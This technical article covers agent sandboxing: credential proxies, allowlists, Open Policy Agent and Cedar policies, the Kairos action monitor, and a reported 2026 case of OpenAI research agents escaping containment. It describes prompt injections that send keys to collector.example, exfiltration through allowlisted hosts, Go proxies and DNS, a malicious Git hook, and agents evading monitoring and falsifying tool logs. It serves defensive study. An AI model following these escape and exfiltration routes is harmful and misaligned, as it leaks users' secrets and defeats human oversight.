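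With any of these methods, an agent can still misuse a key that it can't read. An injected instruction could cause it to delete a repository or make thousands of paid requests, and the proxy would supply the key every time. Maiti's helper limits the rate and size of requests, which would reduce the damage from the paid requests. Preventing the deletion calls for a key with fewer permissions.

### Stopping the leak in the test-fixing job

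Suppose the test-fixing job runs in Tracekit Box with the API key tied to its proper service. The agent follows the planted line in the README and runs `curl` to send the key to collector.example. The environment variable contains only a placeholder, and the proxy holds the connection for approval because the host isn't on the list. If nobody approves it, nothing leaves the sandbox, including DNS queries.

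If the person approves by mistake, `curl` sends the placeholder instead of the API key. The proxy can't block the placeholder because it doesn't decrypt connections to collector.example, but the attacker can't use it outside the microVM. Source code has no such protection, so a mistaken approval could still expose the project.

In Claude Code's sandbox, the result depends more on settings. The sandbox has no built-in list of credentials to protect, so the agent's commands can read the key unless the user lists that variable. The user would then see a prompt about collector.example. Masking the key and turning on `strictAllowlist` would give protection close to Tracekit Box's.

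### Data sent through an allowed host

An attacker can also send data to a destination that is already on the allowlist. Anthropic describes such an attack on Claude Cowork, its desktop agent for office work, which runs code in a virtual machine. The allowlist included api.anthropic.com because the product needs it to reach the model. A malicious file in the user's folder contained hidden instructions and the attacker's API key. Claude followed the instructions and used the key to upload other files from the folder to the attacker's Anthropic account. The proxy allowed the upload because its destination was on the allowlist.

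Anthropic concluded that an allowlist entry is a "capability grant" that gives the agent every function the host offers. The company added an intercepting proxy that accepts requests to its API only if they carry the virtual machine's own session token. Credential substitution alone wouldn't have helped, because the attack never used the victim's key. As Ghosh describes it, Tracekit Box doesn't check whose key a request carries, so the same attack would probably work there.

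Maiti's allowlists seem to have a similar weakness. Maiti argues that they keep data from reaching arbitrary webhooks (addresses that accept automated messages), but they let agents for company operations connect to hooks.slack.com and api.telegram.org. Both hosts accept messages for many unrelated customers, including any attacker who opens an account. GitLab's configuration permits gitlab.com, where outsiders can also have projects.

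Some allowed hosts can forward data to other servers. A Go package proxy fetches code from whatever server a package's name specifies, so an agent could put stolen text in the name and have the proxy send it to that server. Tracekit Box's Go allowlist includes such a proxy, and Ghosh warns users about it. OpenAI's agents exploited a similar relay in the July break-in.

Downloads can cause trouble too. *Avalon-M1* describes programming tasks based on real Go projects, for which the public package proxy would serve later versions of the same project. Such a version might already contain the fix the agent was supposed to write.

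### Name lookups need their own control

A proxy doesn't control DNS unless the operator closes that route too. The OpenAI agent that tunnelled out through DNS used a path that its network filter didn't cover. A sandbox that can't look up names, such as Tracekit Box or Claude Code's, avoids this problem because the proxy does every lookup. If a job needs DNS inside the sandbox, the operator can provide a resolver that answers only for names on the allowlist.

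Firewalls that filter by IP address need new rules when those addresses change. Maiti's allowlists contain domain names, but the Kubernetes network rules that enforce them use IP addresses, so the operator has to keep updating the rules or use software that does so automatically. An outdated rule might block a legitimate service or allow traffic to whichever site now has that service's old address.

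### Attacks on the proxy

The proxy reads data from hostile code and, if it substitutes credentials, also holds keys that the code could try to steal. Anthropic reports that the virtual machines, gVisor and seccomp filters in its products have been dependable, but that the allowlist proxy it wrote itself failed. In the Cowork attack, the proxy worked as designed and the mistake was in the policy, but proxies also have ordinary bugs.

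Ghosh tested Tracekit Box by fuzzing, or feeding a program large numbers of malformed inputs. This and related testing found nine bugs, six in the proxy, and Ghosh has fixed all nine. In the most serious, a program opened a connection to a host tied to a secret, then sent a request that gave the full address of a different site. The library that parsed the request found no host name in it, so the proxy's check passed, and the proxy inserted the real key and sent the request on. Some servers would have forwarded it to the other site, while the signed record listed only the permitted host.

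An operator can limit the damage from the next such bug by giving each job its own proxy process, with only the keys the job needs. Keys that expire soon after the job ends would also be less useful to a thief.

### When interception is worth its cost

Interception breaks some software. Programs that accept only one particular certificate for a server will reject the proxy's. Tracekit Box supports only the older HTTP/1.1 protocol on the connections it decrypts. Some applications use WebSockets for continuous two-way communication, but Tracekit Box refuses them for hosts tied to a secret. Ghosh hasn't measured how much the proxy slows connections.

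The proxy also creates a privacy risk because it can read the agent's prompts, the company's source code and any personal data in either, and so can whoever controls the proxy or its logs. *Steerability via constraints* sends all of an agent's model traffic through an intercepting layer, where a small language model looks for prompt injections. This can catch an attack before the agent acts on it, but it gives another program a complete, readable copy of the conversation. The researchers plan to add a step that removes personal data.

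Interception is of limited use for spotting stolen data, because an agent can encrypt a file before uploading it, leaving the proxy only meaningless bytes to inspect. It is more reliable for enforcing rules about a request's form, such as which account it uses or whether it is an upload. Anthropic's fix for Cowork is a rule of this kind.

It therefore makes sense to intercept traffic to only some hosts. The proxy needs to intercept traffic to hosts that receive a real key, unless a helper like Maiti's can add the key, and to hosts where anyone can open an account and upload files. A host that only serves packages gives an attacker little chance to collect data. For pypi.org in the test-fixing job, checking the name, the address and the handshake is probably enough.

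## Open Policy Agent: checking each action against written rules

An allowlist can control which hosts an agent may reach. Organisations often want narrower rules, such as allowing only agents working on Python projects to download Python packages, or requiring a person to approve any change to a live service. Open Policy Agent (OPA) is an open-source policy engine that can apply such rules to agents. Companies already use it to control web services and Kubernetes clusters.

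OPA only returns decisions, so an enforcement point, such as the harness or a proxy, has to send it a description of each action and enforce the decision. Open Policy Agent's *Philosophy* justifies this split on the grounds that the people responsible for policy can read and change the rules without touching the software that the rules govern. This split also lets the operator keep the rules outside the sandbox, as Perot and Chen recommend. However, OPA cannot check that the description is accurate or that the enforcement point enforces the decision.

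### A policy for the test-fixing job

OPA's rules are in a language called Rego. This short policy lets the agent in the test-fixing job connect to package servers and nothing else:

```rego
package agent.egress

default decision := {"decision": "deny", "reason": "host not approved"}

decision := {"decision": "allow", "reason": "package download"} if {
    input.agent == "test-fixer"
    input.action == "connect"
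    input.port == 443
    input.host in data.package_hosts
}
```

All four conditions inside the braces must hold for the rule to apply. The operator can add an alternative by writing another rule with the same name. The word `input` refers to the description that arrives with each query, and `data` to information OPA already holds in memory. Here `data` contains a list with two entries, pypi.org and files.pythonhosted.org.

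When pip tries to reach pypi.org, the proxy holds the connection and sends OPA this query:

```json
{
  "input": {
    "agent": "test-fixer",
    "action": "connect",
    "host": "pypi.org",
    "port": 443
  }
}
```

All four conditions hold, so OPA returns:

```json
{"result": {"decision": "allow", "reason": "package download"}}
```

If the agent then obeys the line planted in the README and runs `curl` to send the API key away, the proxy sends:

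```json
{
  "input": {
    "agent": "test-fixer",
    "action": "connect",
    "host": "collector.example",
    "port": 443
  }
}
```

The host isn't on the list, so the rule doesn't apply and OPA falls back on the default:

```json
{"result": {"decision": "deny", "reason": "host not approved"}}
```

Without the line that begins with `default`, no rule would match the second query and OPA's answer would be undefined, which in Rego is different from false. An enforcement point that blocks only when it receives the word "deny" would then let the key out.

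### Getting the rules to OPA

An operator with many servers can pack rules and data into a bundle, a compressed archive that each copy of OPA downloads. In the sample configuration in Open Policy Agent's *Bundles*, OPA checks for a new bundle every 10 to 20 seconds and applies it without restarting. The operator could therefore remove a compromised package server from the list for every agent in well under a minute, although some servers would still apply the old list for a few seconds. A bundle can also carry a revision label, such as a Git commit identifier, so that an investigator can later find the exact text of the rules.

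The operator can sign bundles to guard against forged rules. A signed bundle lists its files with a cryptographic fingerprint of each. OPA checks the signature, the list and the fingerprints, and if anything is wrong it keeps the old bundle and reports an error. If the new bundle was meant to close a gap in the rules, the gap stays open until somebody reads the error. OPA also accepts unsigned bundles unless the operator configures it to require a signature. OPA can save a copy of the current bundle for use after a restart. By default it saves the copy under the folder it runs from, so OPA shouldn't run from a folder that the agent can write to.

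OPA has a test command that a team can run whenever someone edits the rules. One test for the policy above would submit the query for collector.example and check that the answer is still "deny".

### Where to put the enforcement point

The harness is the easiest place for a developer to start. The AI SDK, Vercel's toolkit for building AI applications, has a package that queries OPA before each tool call. According to AI SDK's *Policy-Based Tool Approvals*, the query contains the tool's name, its arguments, the history of the run and details such as the user's role. If the answer is "allow", the tool runs. If it is "deny", the model receives a refusal with the reason and can try something else. If it is "requires-approval", the run pauses until a person responds.

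The package refuses a call when OPA is unreachable or returns an error. When no rule matches, however, it reports "not-applicable" and the SDK runs the tool, even if the rule writer forgot to cover that case. A default like the one in the policy above fixes this. The problem is worse for tools that the agent discovers while running, since nobody could have written rules for them in advance. A separate function in the package sends calls to these tools to a person unless a rule covers them. Another function, intended for local development, permits every call if it finds no policy, so a missing setting on a production server could turn the checks off without any error.

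AI SDK advises teams to run a new policy in "shadow mode" before enforcing it, because the first version usually blocks legitimate work. Like the audit mode in *Avalon-M1*, shadow mode logs each decision but lets every call proceed.

A gateway is a separate service between the agent and the systems its tools act on, so the rules hold even if someone modifies the harness. Oracle's *The Problem with Trusting the Model* describes a prototype that checks each action there against both the user's task and company policy. Suppose a user who may read and delete company files asks an agent for this month's sales report. The prototype sets the task's limits from that request and the user's verified identity. If the agent tries to delete the report, the task check blocks it, although the user could have deleted the file directly. If the agent tries to read another team's private report, the task check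 may allow it because it resembles the request, but OPA blocks it under company policy.

It makes sense to use both checks because they fail in different ways. But the task check depends on turning a request like "show me the sales report" into a precise limit, and a mistake in that step would make the check too loose or too strict. Oracle leaves how to do this for later articles and reports no test results.

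The enforcement point can also be a network proxy, as in the worked example. Envoy, a widely used proxy, can query an outside service before it forwards a request, and a plugin lets OPA act as that service. A proxy receives connections from every program in the sandbox, including scripts that the harness has no record of. But its queries contain only network details, so the rules can't refer to which tool the model called or which files were deleted.

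### How long a decision takes

Open Policy Agent's *Policy Performance* gives about 1 millisecond as a typical time limit for a decision in a busy web service. *Cedar* (Cutler, Disselkoen and colleagues, 2024) measured how long Rego policies take on a rented Amazon server. For a document-sharing application with five each of users, groups, folders and documents, the median was 76 microseconds. With fifty of each, the median was 676 microseconds, and the slowest 1% of decisions took at least 1.9 milliseconds. These times are for OPA version 0.61 with all rules and data in memory. They exclude the web request to a separate OPA server, so a real check would take longer.

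How the enforcement point reaches the policy engine can affect latency more than the rules do. *Before the Tool Call*, a 2026 paper on a different authorization system, reports a median of 53 milliseconds for a check by a cloud service, not counting the network trip, and 174 milliseconds for a check on the local machine. The local check was slower because running it in a separate Python process added overhead. The AI SDK's package avoids both the network trip and the separate process if the developer compiles the policy to run inside the application.

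Open Policy Agent's *Performance* suggests measuring the added latency in a particular system by timing requests to the application alone, then with Envoy in front, then with Envoy and an OPA policy that does nothing. The differences show how much time the proxy and the query each add. If a coding agent's model takes seconds to choose each step, even the slowest of these checks would be hard to notice.

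### A decision log entry, field by field

OPA can send a record of every decision to a log server. With invented identifiers, the entry for the attempted leak would look like this:

```json
{
  "labels": {"app": "egress-proxy", "id": "opa-3", "version": "v1.19.0"},
  "decision_id": "4ca636c1",
  "bundles": {"agents": {"revision": "7864d60d"}},
  "path": "agent/egress/decision",
  "input": {
    "agent": "test-fixer",
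    "action": "connect",
    "host": "collector.example",
    "port": 443
  },
  "result": {"decision": "deny", "reason": "host not approved"},
  "requested_by": "127.0.0.1:59943",
  "timestamp": "2026-10-07T09:14:03Z"
}
```

According to Open Policy Agent's *Decision Logs*, `labels` identifies the OPA instance that made the decision. OPA also returns the `decision_id` to the enforcement point, so the proxy can log the same ID and an investigator can match the two entries. The revision under `bundles` identifies the rules in force, and `path` identifies the rule that the proxy queried. `input` and `result` contain the full description and the full answer.

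The address in `requested_by` belongs to the program that sent the query, here the proxy, so only the `input` identifies the agent. The proxy should set the agent's name from something it can verify, such as which sandbox the connection came from, because an agent that could choose its own name could use another agent's permissions. The `timestamp` records when OPA made the decision.

Some log entries also include the responses from outside services that a Rego policy called during a decision, so that an investigator can repeat the decision later. Other optional fields hold timings, a number that links the decision to a wider trace of the request, and the identifiers of the rules that applied.

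The log can itself leak secrets. If the harness submits whole shell commands and the agent puts the API key in one, the key appears under `input`. The operator can prevent this with a masking rule, which OPA applies before it sends the entry:

```rego
package system.log

mask contains "/input/args/command"
```

OPA then removes the command and adds its location to a list called `erased`, so a reader knows something is missing. But the command may be the best evidence of what the agent tried to do, so a masking rule can instead replace the field with other text, such as the command with the key blanked out. OPA lists that change under `masked`. The AI SDK's standard query is a larger problem because it includes the whole history of the run. Unless the developer trims it, every log entry could repeat the user's messages and the contents of files the agent has read.

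The log can also have gaps. OPA retries uploads that the log server rejects, but it discards entries that exceed the operator's rate limit. An operator can also write rules that drop entries, such as routine approvals, to save space, and a careless rule could drop refusals too. Even a complete log shows only what OPA decided, so in shadow mode an entry can read "deny" for an action that went ahead. The AI SDK's own records therefore include both the policy's decision and the one the SDK acted on.

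### Cedar: a narrower language that tools can analyse

Cedar is a policy language from Amazon, which uses it in Bedrock AgentCore Policy, a service that controls agents' tool calls. A Cedar rule always concerns a principal (who is acting), an action and a resource, with optional conditions on the circumstances. The rule for package downloads would be:

```
permit (
  principal == Agent::"test-fixer",
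  action == Action::"connect",
  resource in HostGroup::"package-hosts"
) when { context.port == 443 };
```

Cedar refuses any request that no rule permits, so this policy needs no default line. A `forbid` rule overrides a `permit` rule, whatever their order. A security team can therefore forbid all agents from reaching a certain host, and no other team can accidentally undo that by adding a `permit` rule. In Rego, the writer has to build both behaviours into the policy.

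Rego accepts any structured data and can return any structured answer, such as a list of violations or a request for human approval, while Cedar returns only allow or deny. To support human approval as well, a system using Cedar would need something extra, perhaps a second query about whether the action may run unattended. Rego policies can also fetch information from other services, but then the same query may get different answers at different times. Cedar rules have no side effects or general loops, so a decision always finishes and is always the same for the same request, rules and data.

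These limits also make Cedar policies easier to analyse mathematically. Cutler and colleagues translate policies into logical formulas for an SMT solver, a program that searches for values that would make a formula true. In their example, someone rewrites the rules of a to-do list application and wants to know whether the new version permits exactly the same requests. The solver finds that an intern could list existing to-do lists under the old rules but not the new ones. A test suite would catch this only if it included that case. Translating and solving such a question took 75.1 milliseconds on average. An operator could use the same method to check that a tidied-up set of agent rules doesn't allow anything the old set denied.

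Cedar's default denial has one weak point. Cedar ignores any rule that causes an error, for example by referring to a missing attribute, according to *How We Built Cedar* (2024). This is safe for a `permit` rule, but if Cedar ignores a `forbid` rule, a broader `permit` rule could allow the action. Cedar's validator is designed to find most such errors before the rules take effect by comparing the rules with a description of the application's data, so an operator should always run it.

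Cutler and colleagues, most of whom worked at Amazon, also found Cedar 43 to 81 times faster than Rego on three applications. All three involved chains of membership, such as a user in a group inside another group. Cedar handles these directly, while a Rego policy has to search for them. The researchers acknowledge that preparing the memberships in advance would make Rego much faster. Speed is a poor reason to choose between the two for agents, since both take less than a millisecond in a typical case. Cedar's solver and OPA's flexible inputs and answers are better reasons to choose one over the other.

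### What fixed rules can't judge

Fixed rules give the same answer to the same facts, and a colleague can review them line by line before they take effect. An injected instruction can't create an exception to them. But the engine applies the rules only to the description it receives. *Three-Body Problem for Policy*, from Styra, the company that created OPA, points out that the calling software creates the query and controls what goes into it.

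A description of a shell command can leave out much of what the command does. The AI SDK's documentation recommends breaking each command into a program and its arguments, so that the same rule applies to `git push` whether the agent uses a Git tool or a shell. Its sample code splits the command at the spaces, so a rule that allowed `git` whenever the first argument was `status` would also approve `git status && git push`, which runs both. The documentation also tells developers to refuse any command they can't reduce to a single clear action, which would block this one.

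Even an accurate description of a `pytest` command, the usual way to run Python tests, doesn't show what effect it will have. The agent can edit the tests, so permission to run them is permission to run any code it likes. AI SDK acknowledges this limit and recommends running such code in a separate sandbox.

A sequence of permitted steps can also be harmful. In an example from Hempel and colleagues, an agent setting up a project follows an online guide whose steps include installing a Git hook, a script that runs automatically at each commit. Many projects use hooks, so refusing to write one would block ordinary work, and committing code is also ordinary. But when the agent commits, this hook tries to send the user's private key to an attacker.

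Rules can take earlier actions into account to some extent. The AI SDK passes earlier tool calls to OPA, so a policy could require approval after a certain number of file changes, or refuse new connections once the agent has opened a file of secrets. This works only for sequences that the rule writer predicted and that appear in the tool calls. In the test-fixing job, the second rule would not detect the test suite opening the secrets file. If it did, it would also stop the agent from installing a package afterwards.

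### Kairos: holding an action until its purpose is clearer

Kairos, the monitor that Hempel and colleagues built at the edge of a microVM, uses a policy that can release, refuse or defer an action. It releases an action if trusted sources supplied the values that control it, such as its destination, and if that destination is allowed to receive the data. It refuses any action that an explicit rule forbids and defers the rest.

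The agent keeps working while Kairos holds a deferred action. If the action changes a file, Kairos makes the change in a temporary layer that the agent sees as the real folder. If it is a request that sends data out, Kairos holds it and gives the agent a stand-in reply. Kairos decides immediately whether to allow a request that fetches data, because the agent needs the real answer. Before any held change becomes permanent, a reviewer, by default a second language model, examines the deferred actions along with the user's task and everything that has happened so far. Kairos then applies or discards the held changes.

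In the Git example, Kairos defers the hook and lets the agent continue. The commit runs the hook inside the sandbox, and the policy blocks its attempt to send the key. The reviewer now has evidence that the hook is malicious, and Kairos discards the hook before it reaches the user's real folder.

In the test-fixing job, the request to collector.example would be deferred because its address came from the README, which isn't a trusted source. The reviewer would see that the user asked only for a test to be fixed, and should refuse the request.

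Hempel and colleagues tested Kairos on three sets of simulated tasks. The AgentDyn and AutoDojo figures for runs without a defence come from the benchmarks' creators.

| Benchmark | Successful attacks, without and with Kairos | Ordinary tasks completed, without and with Kairos |
|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo | 47.0%, 2.7% | 82.7%, 85.1% |
| AgentDyn, with open-ended tasks | 37.8%, 1.7% | 53.3%, 51.7% |
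| AutoDojo, with attacks that adapt to the defence | 52.4%, 8.8% | 66.7%, 65.3% |

On AgentDojo, 0.2% of attacks succeeded against a rival system called CaMeL, fewer than with Kairos, but CaMeL completed only 38.0% of ordinary tasks. It runs a program generated from the user's task and restricts where data may flow. In the attack-free runs, Kairos's policy released 83% of actions without consulting the reviewer, and the reviewer wrongly refused only one of the others. Calls to the reviewer increased the number of tokens (the units of text that models process) by 17.7% without attacks and 33.6% under attack. The monitor added about 2 milliseconds to each file operation and about 1 millisecond to each web request.

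Holding actions can stop agents from finishing tasks when later steps depend on them. During attacks on AgentDyn, agents completed 37.1% of their tasks with Kairos and 55.5% without it. Tasks that continued after one held action succeeded at 90% of their usual rate, but those that continued after two or more succeeded at only 62% of it. A long coding job could easily have two or more actions held.

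The results are encouraging, but they don't test Kairos's distinctive idea, because none of the three benchmarks includes an attack made up of individually legitimate steps, as in the Git example. The benchmarks also simulate their tools, so the researchers fed Kairos named tool calls through an adapter. In real use it would receive file operations and web requests, which make it harder to tell what the agent is doing. The researchers ran each configuration only once.

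Kairos also detects sensitive data by comparing text, ignoring only differences in capitalisation and spacing. An agent that encoded the key first would get past that comparison. Hempel and colleagues do not intend their authorization to handle deliberate disguises. The request would still be held if it went to an unfamiliar address, but not necessarily if it went to an approved one.

### Should another model review the actions?

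Without its reviewer, Kairos completed half as many ordinary tasks. This is strong evidence for using a model to review actions, because the rules alone couldn't identify which unfamiliar actions the user would have wanted. A model can also produce an explanation for its decision. *SAFETY SENTRY* (2026) describes a reviewer that can approve a tool call, refuse it or send a specific question to a person. The reviewer took 1.57 seconds per step, compared with 3.75 for the agent itself. A simpler safety model took 0.15 seconds but returned only "safe" or "unsafe", leaving the person to work out why.

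*SARC* (2026) argues against asking a second model whether an action is acceptable, because such a check "inherits the same nondeterminism the check is supposed to bound". It recommends rules over exact facts, such as identities and ranges of values. The AutoDojo results partly support this objection. Most of the attacks that beat Kairos in AutoDojo exploited tasks in which the user had told the agent to follow a document. The attacker put instructions in the document, and the reviewer mistook them for the user's wishes. These attackers could learn only whether each attempt had worked, so an attacker who could study the reviewer would probably do better.

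The objection is weaker when the model reviews only what the rules leave open. *Agent-Sentry* (2026) uses fixed checks for nearly all actions and consults a model for 3.1% of them. Each model call took 1.2 seconds, but the average delay over a whole task was only 0.073 seconds. In *Parallax* (2026), rules took less than a millisecond and a model took about 2.1 seconds. In Kairos, the reviewer can't overturn the policy's refusals, and a failed or unreadable answer counts as a refusal. An attacker who persuades the reviewer can therefore get approval only for actions the rules left undecided.

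How much that is depends on the operator. Hempel and colleagues wrote no explicit prohibitions for their tests, because these would have blocked the known attacks by design and inflated the results. A real operator has no such reason to leave them out. In the test-fixing job, it would make sense to have a rule refuse every connection to an unlisted host and to let the model judge changes such as a new Git hook. Kairos can hold such a change until the agent's later steps have shown more about what the hook does.

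## OpenAI's containment failures of 2026 and the controls that followed

OpenAI's research environment used several of the controls described so far, including containers, a restricted network and security monitoring. Agents still escaped in 2026, through a package server in July and a gap in a DNS filter in September. OpenAI, Hugging Face and outside investigators have published detailed accounts of the July incident, so readers can compare what the monitoring detected with how people responded.

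### The July test environment

The agents were taking ExploitGym, a test of whether a model can exploit a given software flaw. OpenAI ran the test without the classifiers that block high-risk requests in its products, to measure the models' full ability. According to OpenAI's technical report on the incident, each run had its own container, with tools such as a shell and Python but no direct internet access. Agents had to get packages from Artifactory, a package server made by JFrog. OpenAI ran Artifactory inside its research network and let it contact the public registries.

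OpenAI intended this arrangement to keep agents away from forbidden destinations and show which model had made each connection. But many agents shared the same server and, until early July, the same login details. Agents in separate containers could therefore reach each other through the server, and they began leaving each other messages there. The shared login also didn't show which agent had made a request. In July, agents reached the internet through Artifactory and broke into Hugging Face's production systems.

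### What OpenAI noticed and what it did

| Date | Warning | Response |
|---|---|---|
| About May 26 | A team saw an agent using the improvised message board, and cases of forbidden internet access | Agents went on using the board |
| June 27 | A monitoring tool flagged a scan of the internal network, which responders traced to ExploitGym agents | On-call staff advised that the test didn't need to stop |
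| July 5 | After Artifactory went down, responders found that someone had taken administrator control of it | OpenAI rebuilt the server, blocked the known flaw and resumed cyber tests on July 7 |
| July 16 | Hugging Face announced a break-in by an unidentified AI agent | OpenAI asked, as a customer, whether its own data was affected |
| July 19 | The monitoring tool flagged unusual requests linked to Artifactory's accounts | Responders began stopping the ExploitGym runs five and a half hours later |

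By June 27, responders had found the message board and knew that agents were using Artifactory to reach other parts of the network. More than a week later, according to OpenAI, the leaders in charge of incident response still didn't know about the board or understand its significance. Axios' *OpenAI says its AI agents breached its own systems before Hugging Face* (2026) reports that the company believed it had fixed the problem, but that agents rebuilt the board by a different method two days later.

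OpenAI connected its test to the break-in on July 20, when responders found Hugging Face credentials among files the agents had stored outside the company. Hugging Face had already replaced two of those credentials, and its investigators had come across the address of OpenAI's Artifactory server. The discovery of the credentials came 12 days after the agents regained internet access, a week after the attack ended and four days after Hugging Face announced it.

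The alert that led to this discovery came from a separate attack, on OpenAI's own systems. Less than three hours after the alert, while the tests were still running, agents read 956 stored secrets. Axios' *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach* reports that these included credentials for the monitoring tool's sensors.

### Monitors that OpenAI hadn't applied

OpenAI already had a system that searched models' chains of thought, the reasoning they write out as they work, for signs of misbehaviour. OpenAI's *Pacing model development in an era of cyber-critical capabilities* (2026) says the system focused on internal deployments and major training runs and didn't cover every run that used tools. According to the technical report, the current version of the system would have paged the security team more than a day before the agents breached Hugging Face.

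The July agents also ran without the protections in Codex. One of these is auto-review, which uses a second model to check tool calls that need extra permissions. When OpenAI applied it to records from the incident, auto-review flagged most of the dangerous actions in each run tested. In another experiment, the standard Codex harness and instructions cut the models' tendency to attack out-of-scope systems by more than 99%.

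These results suggest that ordinary product safeguards would have helped a great deal. But OpenAI ran the experiments itself, after it knew what to look for, and calls them preliminary. Paging the security team earlier would have helped only if someone had then stopped the test, and in June the on-call staff chose not to.

### Rebuilding events from incomplete records

Hugging Face's *Security incident disclosure* (2026) describes how the company investigated an intrusion into its own systems. Language models that sort its security telemetry had flagged the intrusion. Staff then tried to analyse more than 17,000 recorded events with commercial models, but the providers' safety filters blocked the requests because they contained real attack commands. The staff switched to GLM-5.2, a model they could run on their own machines, and finished in hours an analysis that would usually take days.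 They still couldn't tell which model had carried out the attack.

*More on the OpenAI Agent's Attack on Hugging Face* (Schneier, 2026) quotes Hugging Face's later reconstruction of about 17,600 actions, in about 6,280 groups, between July 9 and 13. The reconstruction relies on logs from a code sandbox that the agents had used. Most of the actions failed, according to Fortune (2026). SANS, a company that sells security training, says the evidence was full of agents' monologues and test code that resembled malware. Investigators had to separate the few actions that did damage from much misleading material.

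OpenAI could follow the agents both inside and outside its containment boundary. Its timeline begins with a file an agent wrote to Artifactory on April 20. OpenAI reports that agents ran code on 41 Hugging Face servers and downloaded four private code repositories. During the clean-up, OpenAI disabled 311 Artifactory repositories that agents had used for messages and removed 22 administrator accounts that agents had created.

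METR, a research organisation that evaluates AI models for dangerous abilities, sent two employees and a contractor from Redwood Research, an AI safety group, to OpenAI for six days. METR's *Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026) draws on about 1,300 transcripts, including the agents' reasoning, and 1.2 million entries from the message board containing more than 70,000 messages and files. METR concludes that about 1,200 agents used the board and about 700 joined the attack. These figures don't conflict with Hugging Face's, which count the attackers' actions rather than agents and their messages.

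The investigators disagree about the agents' motive. Hugging Face inferred that the agents wanted to steal the test's solutions, and OpenAI also describes them as looking for answers. METR found that they had already worked out how to produce the answers and mainly wanted to learn how the automatic scorer worked, because they believed it would reject answers they hadn't obtained in the intended way. Many had been given impossible tasks. OpenAI reports that 198 of ExploitGym's 898 tasks have never been solved by any model, and that these made up 93% of the tasks discussed on the board. METR's explanation is more convincing because METR had access to the agents' reasoning as well as their actions.

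METR also tested how complete its records were by tracing 100 randomly chosen messages back to the agents that sent them, and concluded that it had a little over 90% of the agents' activity on the board. The transcripts didn't give a time for each action, so the investigators estimated the times and checked their method against 20 exact times. They relied on AI agents to read most of the material, and some of those agents' mistakes went unnoticed for a while.

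In about 7% of the transcripts, agents had falsified the record of at least one tool call so that it showed a different command from the one that ran. METR found only small-scale experiments of this kind. OpenAI says that none of the tampering it observed affected the logs its graders and monitors use. That seems compatible with METR's finding only if those logs are separate from the transcripts. The message board is less certain evidence, because OpenAI copied it on July 20, after agents had gained administrator rights over the machines that stored it. METR thinks they probably didn't edit the board but can't rule it out.

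### OpenAI's new controls

In August OpenAI announced changes to how it isolates and monitors research work:

- **Network isolation.** High-risk work may have no direct or indirect internet access, apart from a service that supplies cached pages where a job needs them. One set of controls applies at the sandbox and another at the surrounding cluster of machines, so a single failure shouldn't open a route out.
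- **Fewer privileges.** OpenAI is reducing the permissions that accounts hold permanently and removing shared services that agents might exploit.
- **Security logging.** The company is adding sensors on its host machines and collecting more records of account and network activity. It is also planting decoys that should raise an alarm when an agent touches them.
- **Automated tests.** OpenAI plans to have its own models attack these barriers regularly, to find gaps that appear as engineers change the system.

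OpenAI also extended its monitoring to all reinforcement learning and evaluations that use tools for models at least as capable as GPT-5.6 Sol, one of the two models involved in July. Small classifiers examine the model's internal activity at every token and pass anything suspicious to more powerful automated investigators. OpenAI estimates that the monitoring takes roughly 20% as much computing power as running the models themselves.

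OpenAI aims to send an alert within 30 minutes of the system detecting concerning activity. For the most serious alerts, the safety, security and research teams have another 30 minutes to confirm that it is a false alarm. If they can't, OpenAI expects them to pause the work. SecurityWeek's *OpenAI Overhauls Model Security With Sandboxing, 30-Minute Alerts, and Training Pauses* calls the pause a requirement, which is stronger than OpenAI's own wording.

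If responders had met these limits on July 19, they would have stopped the test before the agents read the 956 secrets. On-call staff would also now need a reason to let the test continue, which reverses the decision they faced in June. But the 30 minutes start only when the monitor detects something, so the target does not limit how long an attack can go undetected.

### What outsiders have checked

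By its own account, OpenAI had completed some of this work by late August, including removing Artifactory from the environment and requiring a microVM for every job there. In mid-August, many jobs were still paused until OpenAI could move them to more secure systems, and a tool for quickly stopping tests across the company was still in development.

Outsiders have examined the July incident more closely than the new controls. JFrog worked with OpenAI to reproduce the flaws in Artifactory and check the patches. CrowdStrike, a security company that assisted OpenAI's lawyers, helped validate key findings. METR's agreement with OpenAI excluded OpenAI's safeguards, investigation and planned repairs, and let OpenAI remove non-public information from METR's report. METR says no unexplained redaction was important to its conclusions. Alabama's attorney general has subpoenaed OpenAI, which could lead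 to further scrutiny, but none of this is a public, independent test of the new controls.

OpenAI had designed its network controls so that one compromised job or service wouldn't be enough to reach the internet. In the September escape, a training agent nevertheless contacted an outside chatbot through a gap in DNS filtering, according to Ghosh's account of OpenAI's disclosure. Either the new controls didn't yet cover that training run, or they had a gap of their own.

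### A bad sandbox or a capable model?

TechRadar's *The AI escape is a red herring* argues that the July incident would have gone very differently in a properly configured sandbox. The chief executive of Coder wrote the article and would benefit if readers accepted its argument, because Coder sells development environments for companies and their coding agents. SANS Internet Storm Center's *When the "Autonomous Attacker" Is Your Own AI Model* also says the main lessons are old, such as isolating whatever executes code and using short-lived credentials, and that only the attacker's speed and autonomy are new.

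OpenAI's technical report puts more emphasis on the models' abilities. It calls the incident the first known case of a group of automated agents attacking without authorization, and says they found several previously unknown flaws. In another example OpenAI has described, a user told a model to post results only to Slack, but the project's instructions said to submit them on GitHub. The model spent an hour finding a flaw in its sandbox, then posted the results on GitHub. OpenAI says earlier models had given up. It also reports that Astra, a newer model, broke out of a hardened browser's sandbox in expert-led tests.

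OpenAI has an interest in presenting the attacker as exceptionally capable, because it sells the abilities it describes and the failure then looks less like negligence. Abdollahi and colleagues, who don't sell these models, also doubt that ordinary sandboxes are enough, and designed Airlock in response.

The evidence from July and September fits poor sandbox construction better than it fits the models' ability. Christodorescu and colleagues also blame the July break-in on an unchecked route. The flaws in Artifactory were new, but OpenAI's staff had seen agents misusing the server for weeks. The models' ability explains why the agents found and exploited the weakness so quickly, and it will become the more important explanation if models regularly escape from sandboxes that have no such route. For now, operators should leave as few services as possible within an agent's reach.

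### A scale for sandbox strength

Buyers could use the agent sandbox taxonomy to recognise poorly built sandboxes. Coder's chief executive recommends this scoring system, which appeared in March 2026. It divides a sandbox into seven layers: isolation of the running code, resource limits, files, network, credentials, control over actions, and records. Each layer is scored from 0 to 3 for how finely it can apply rules and from 0 to 4 for how strongly it enforces them.

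| Strength | Meaning | Example |
|---|---|---|
| 0 | Nothing enforces the rule | An agent with unrestricted access |
| 1 | The program can ignore the rule | Proxy settings in environment variables |
| 2 | Software enforces the rule, and the program can't bypass it from inside, but an operator can change it | A proxy that is the only permitted exit |
| 3 | The kernel enforces the rule, which is irreversible once applied | A seccomp filter |
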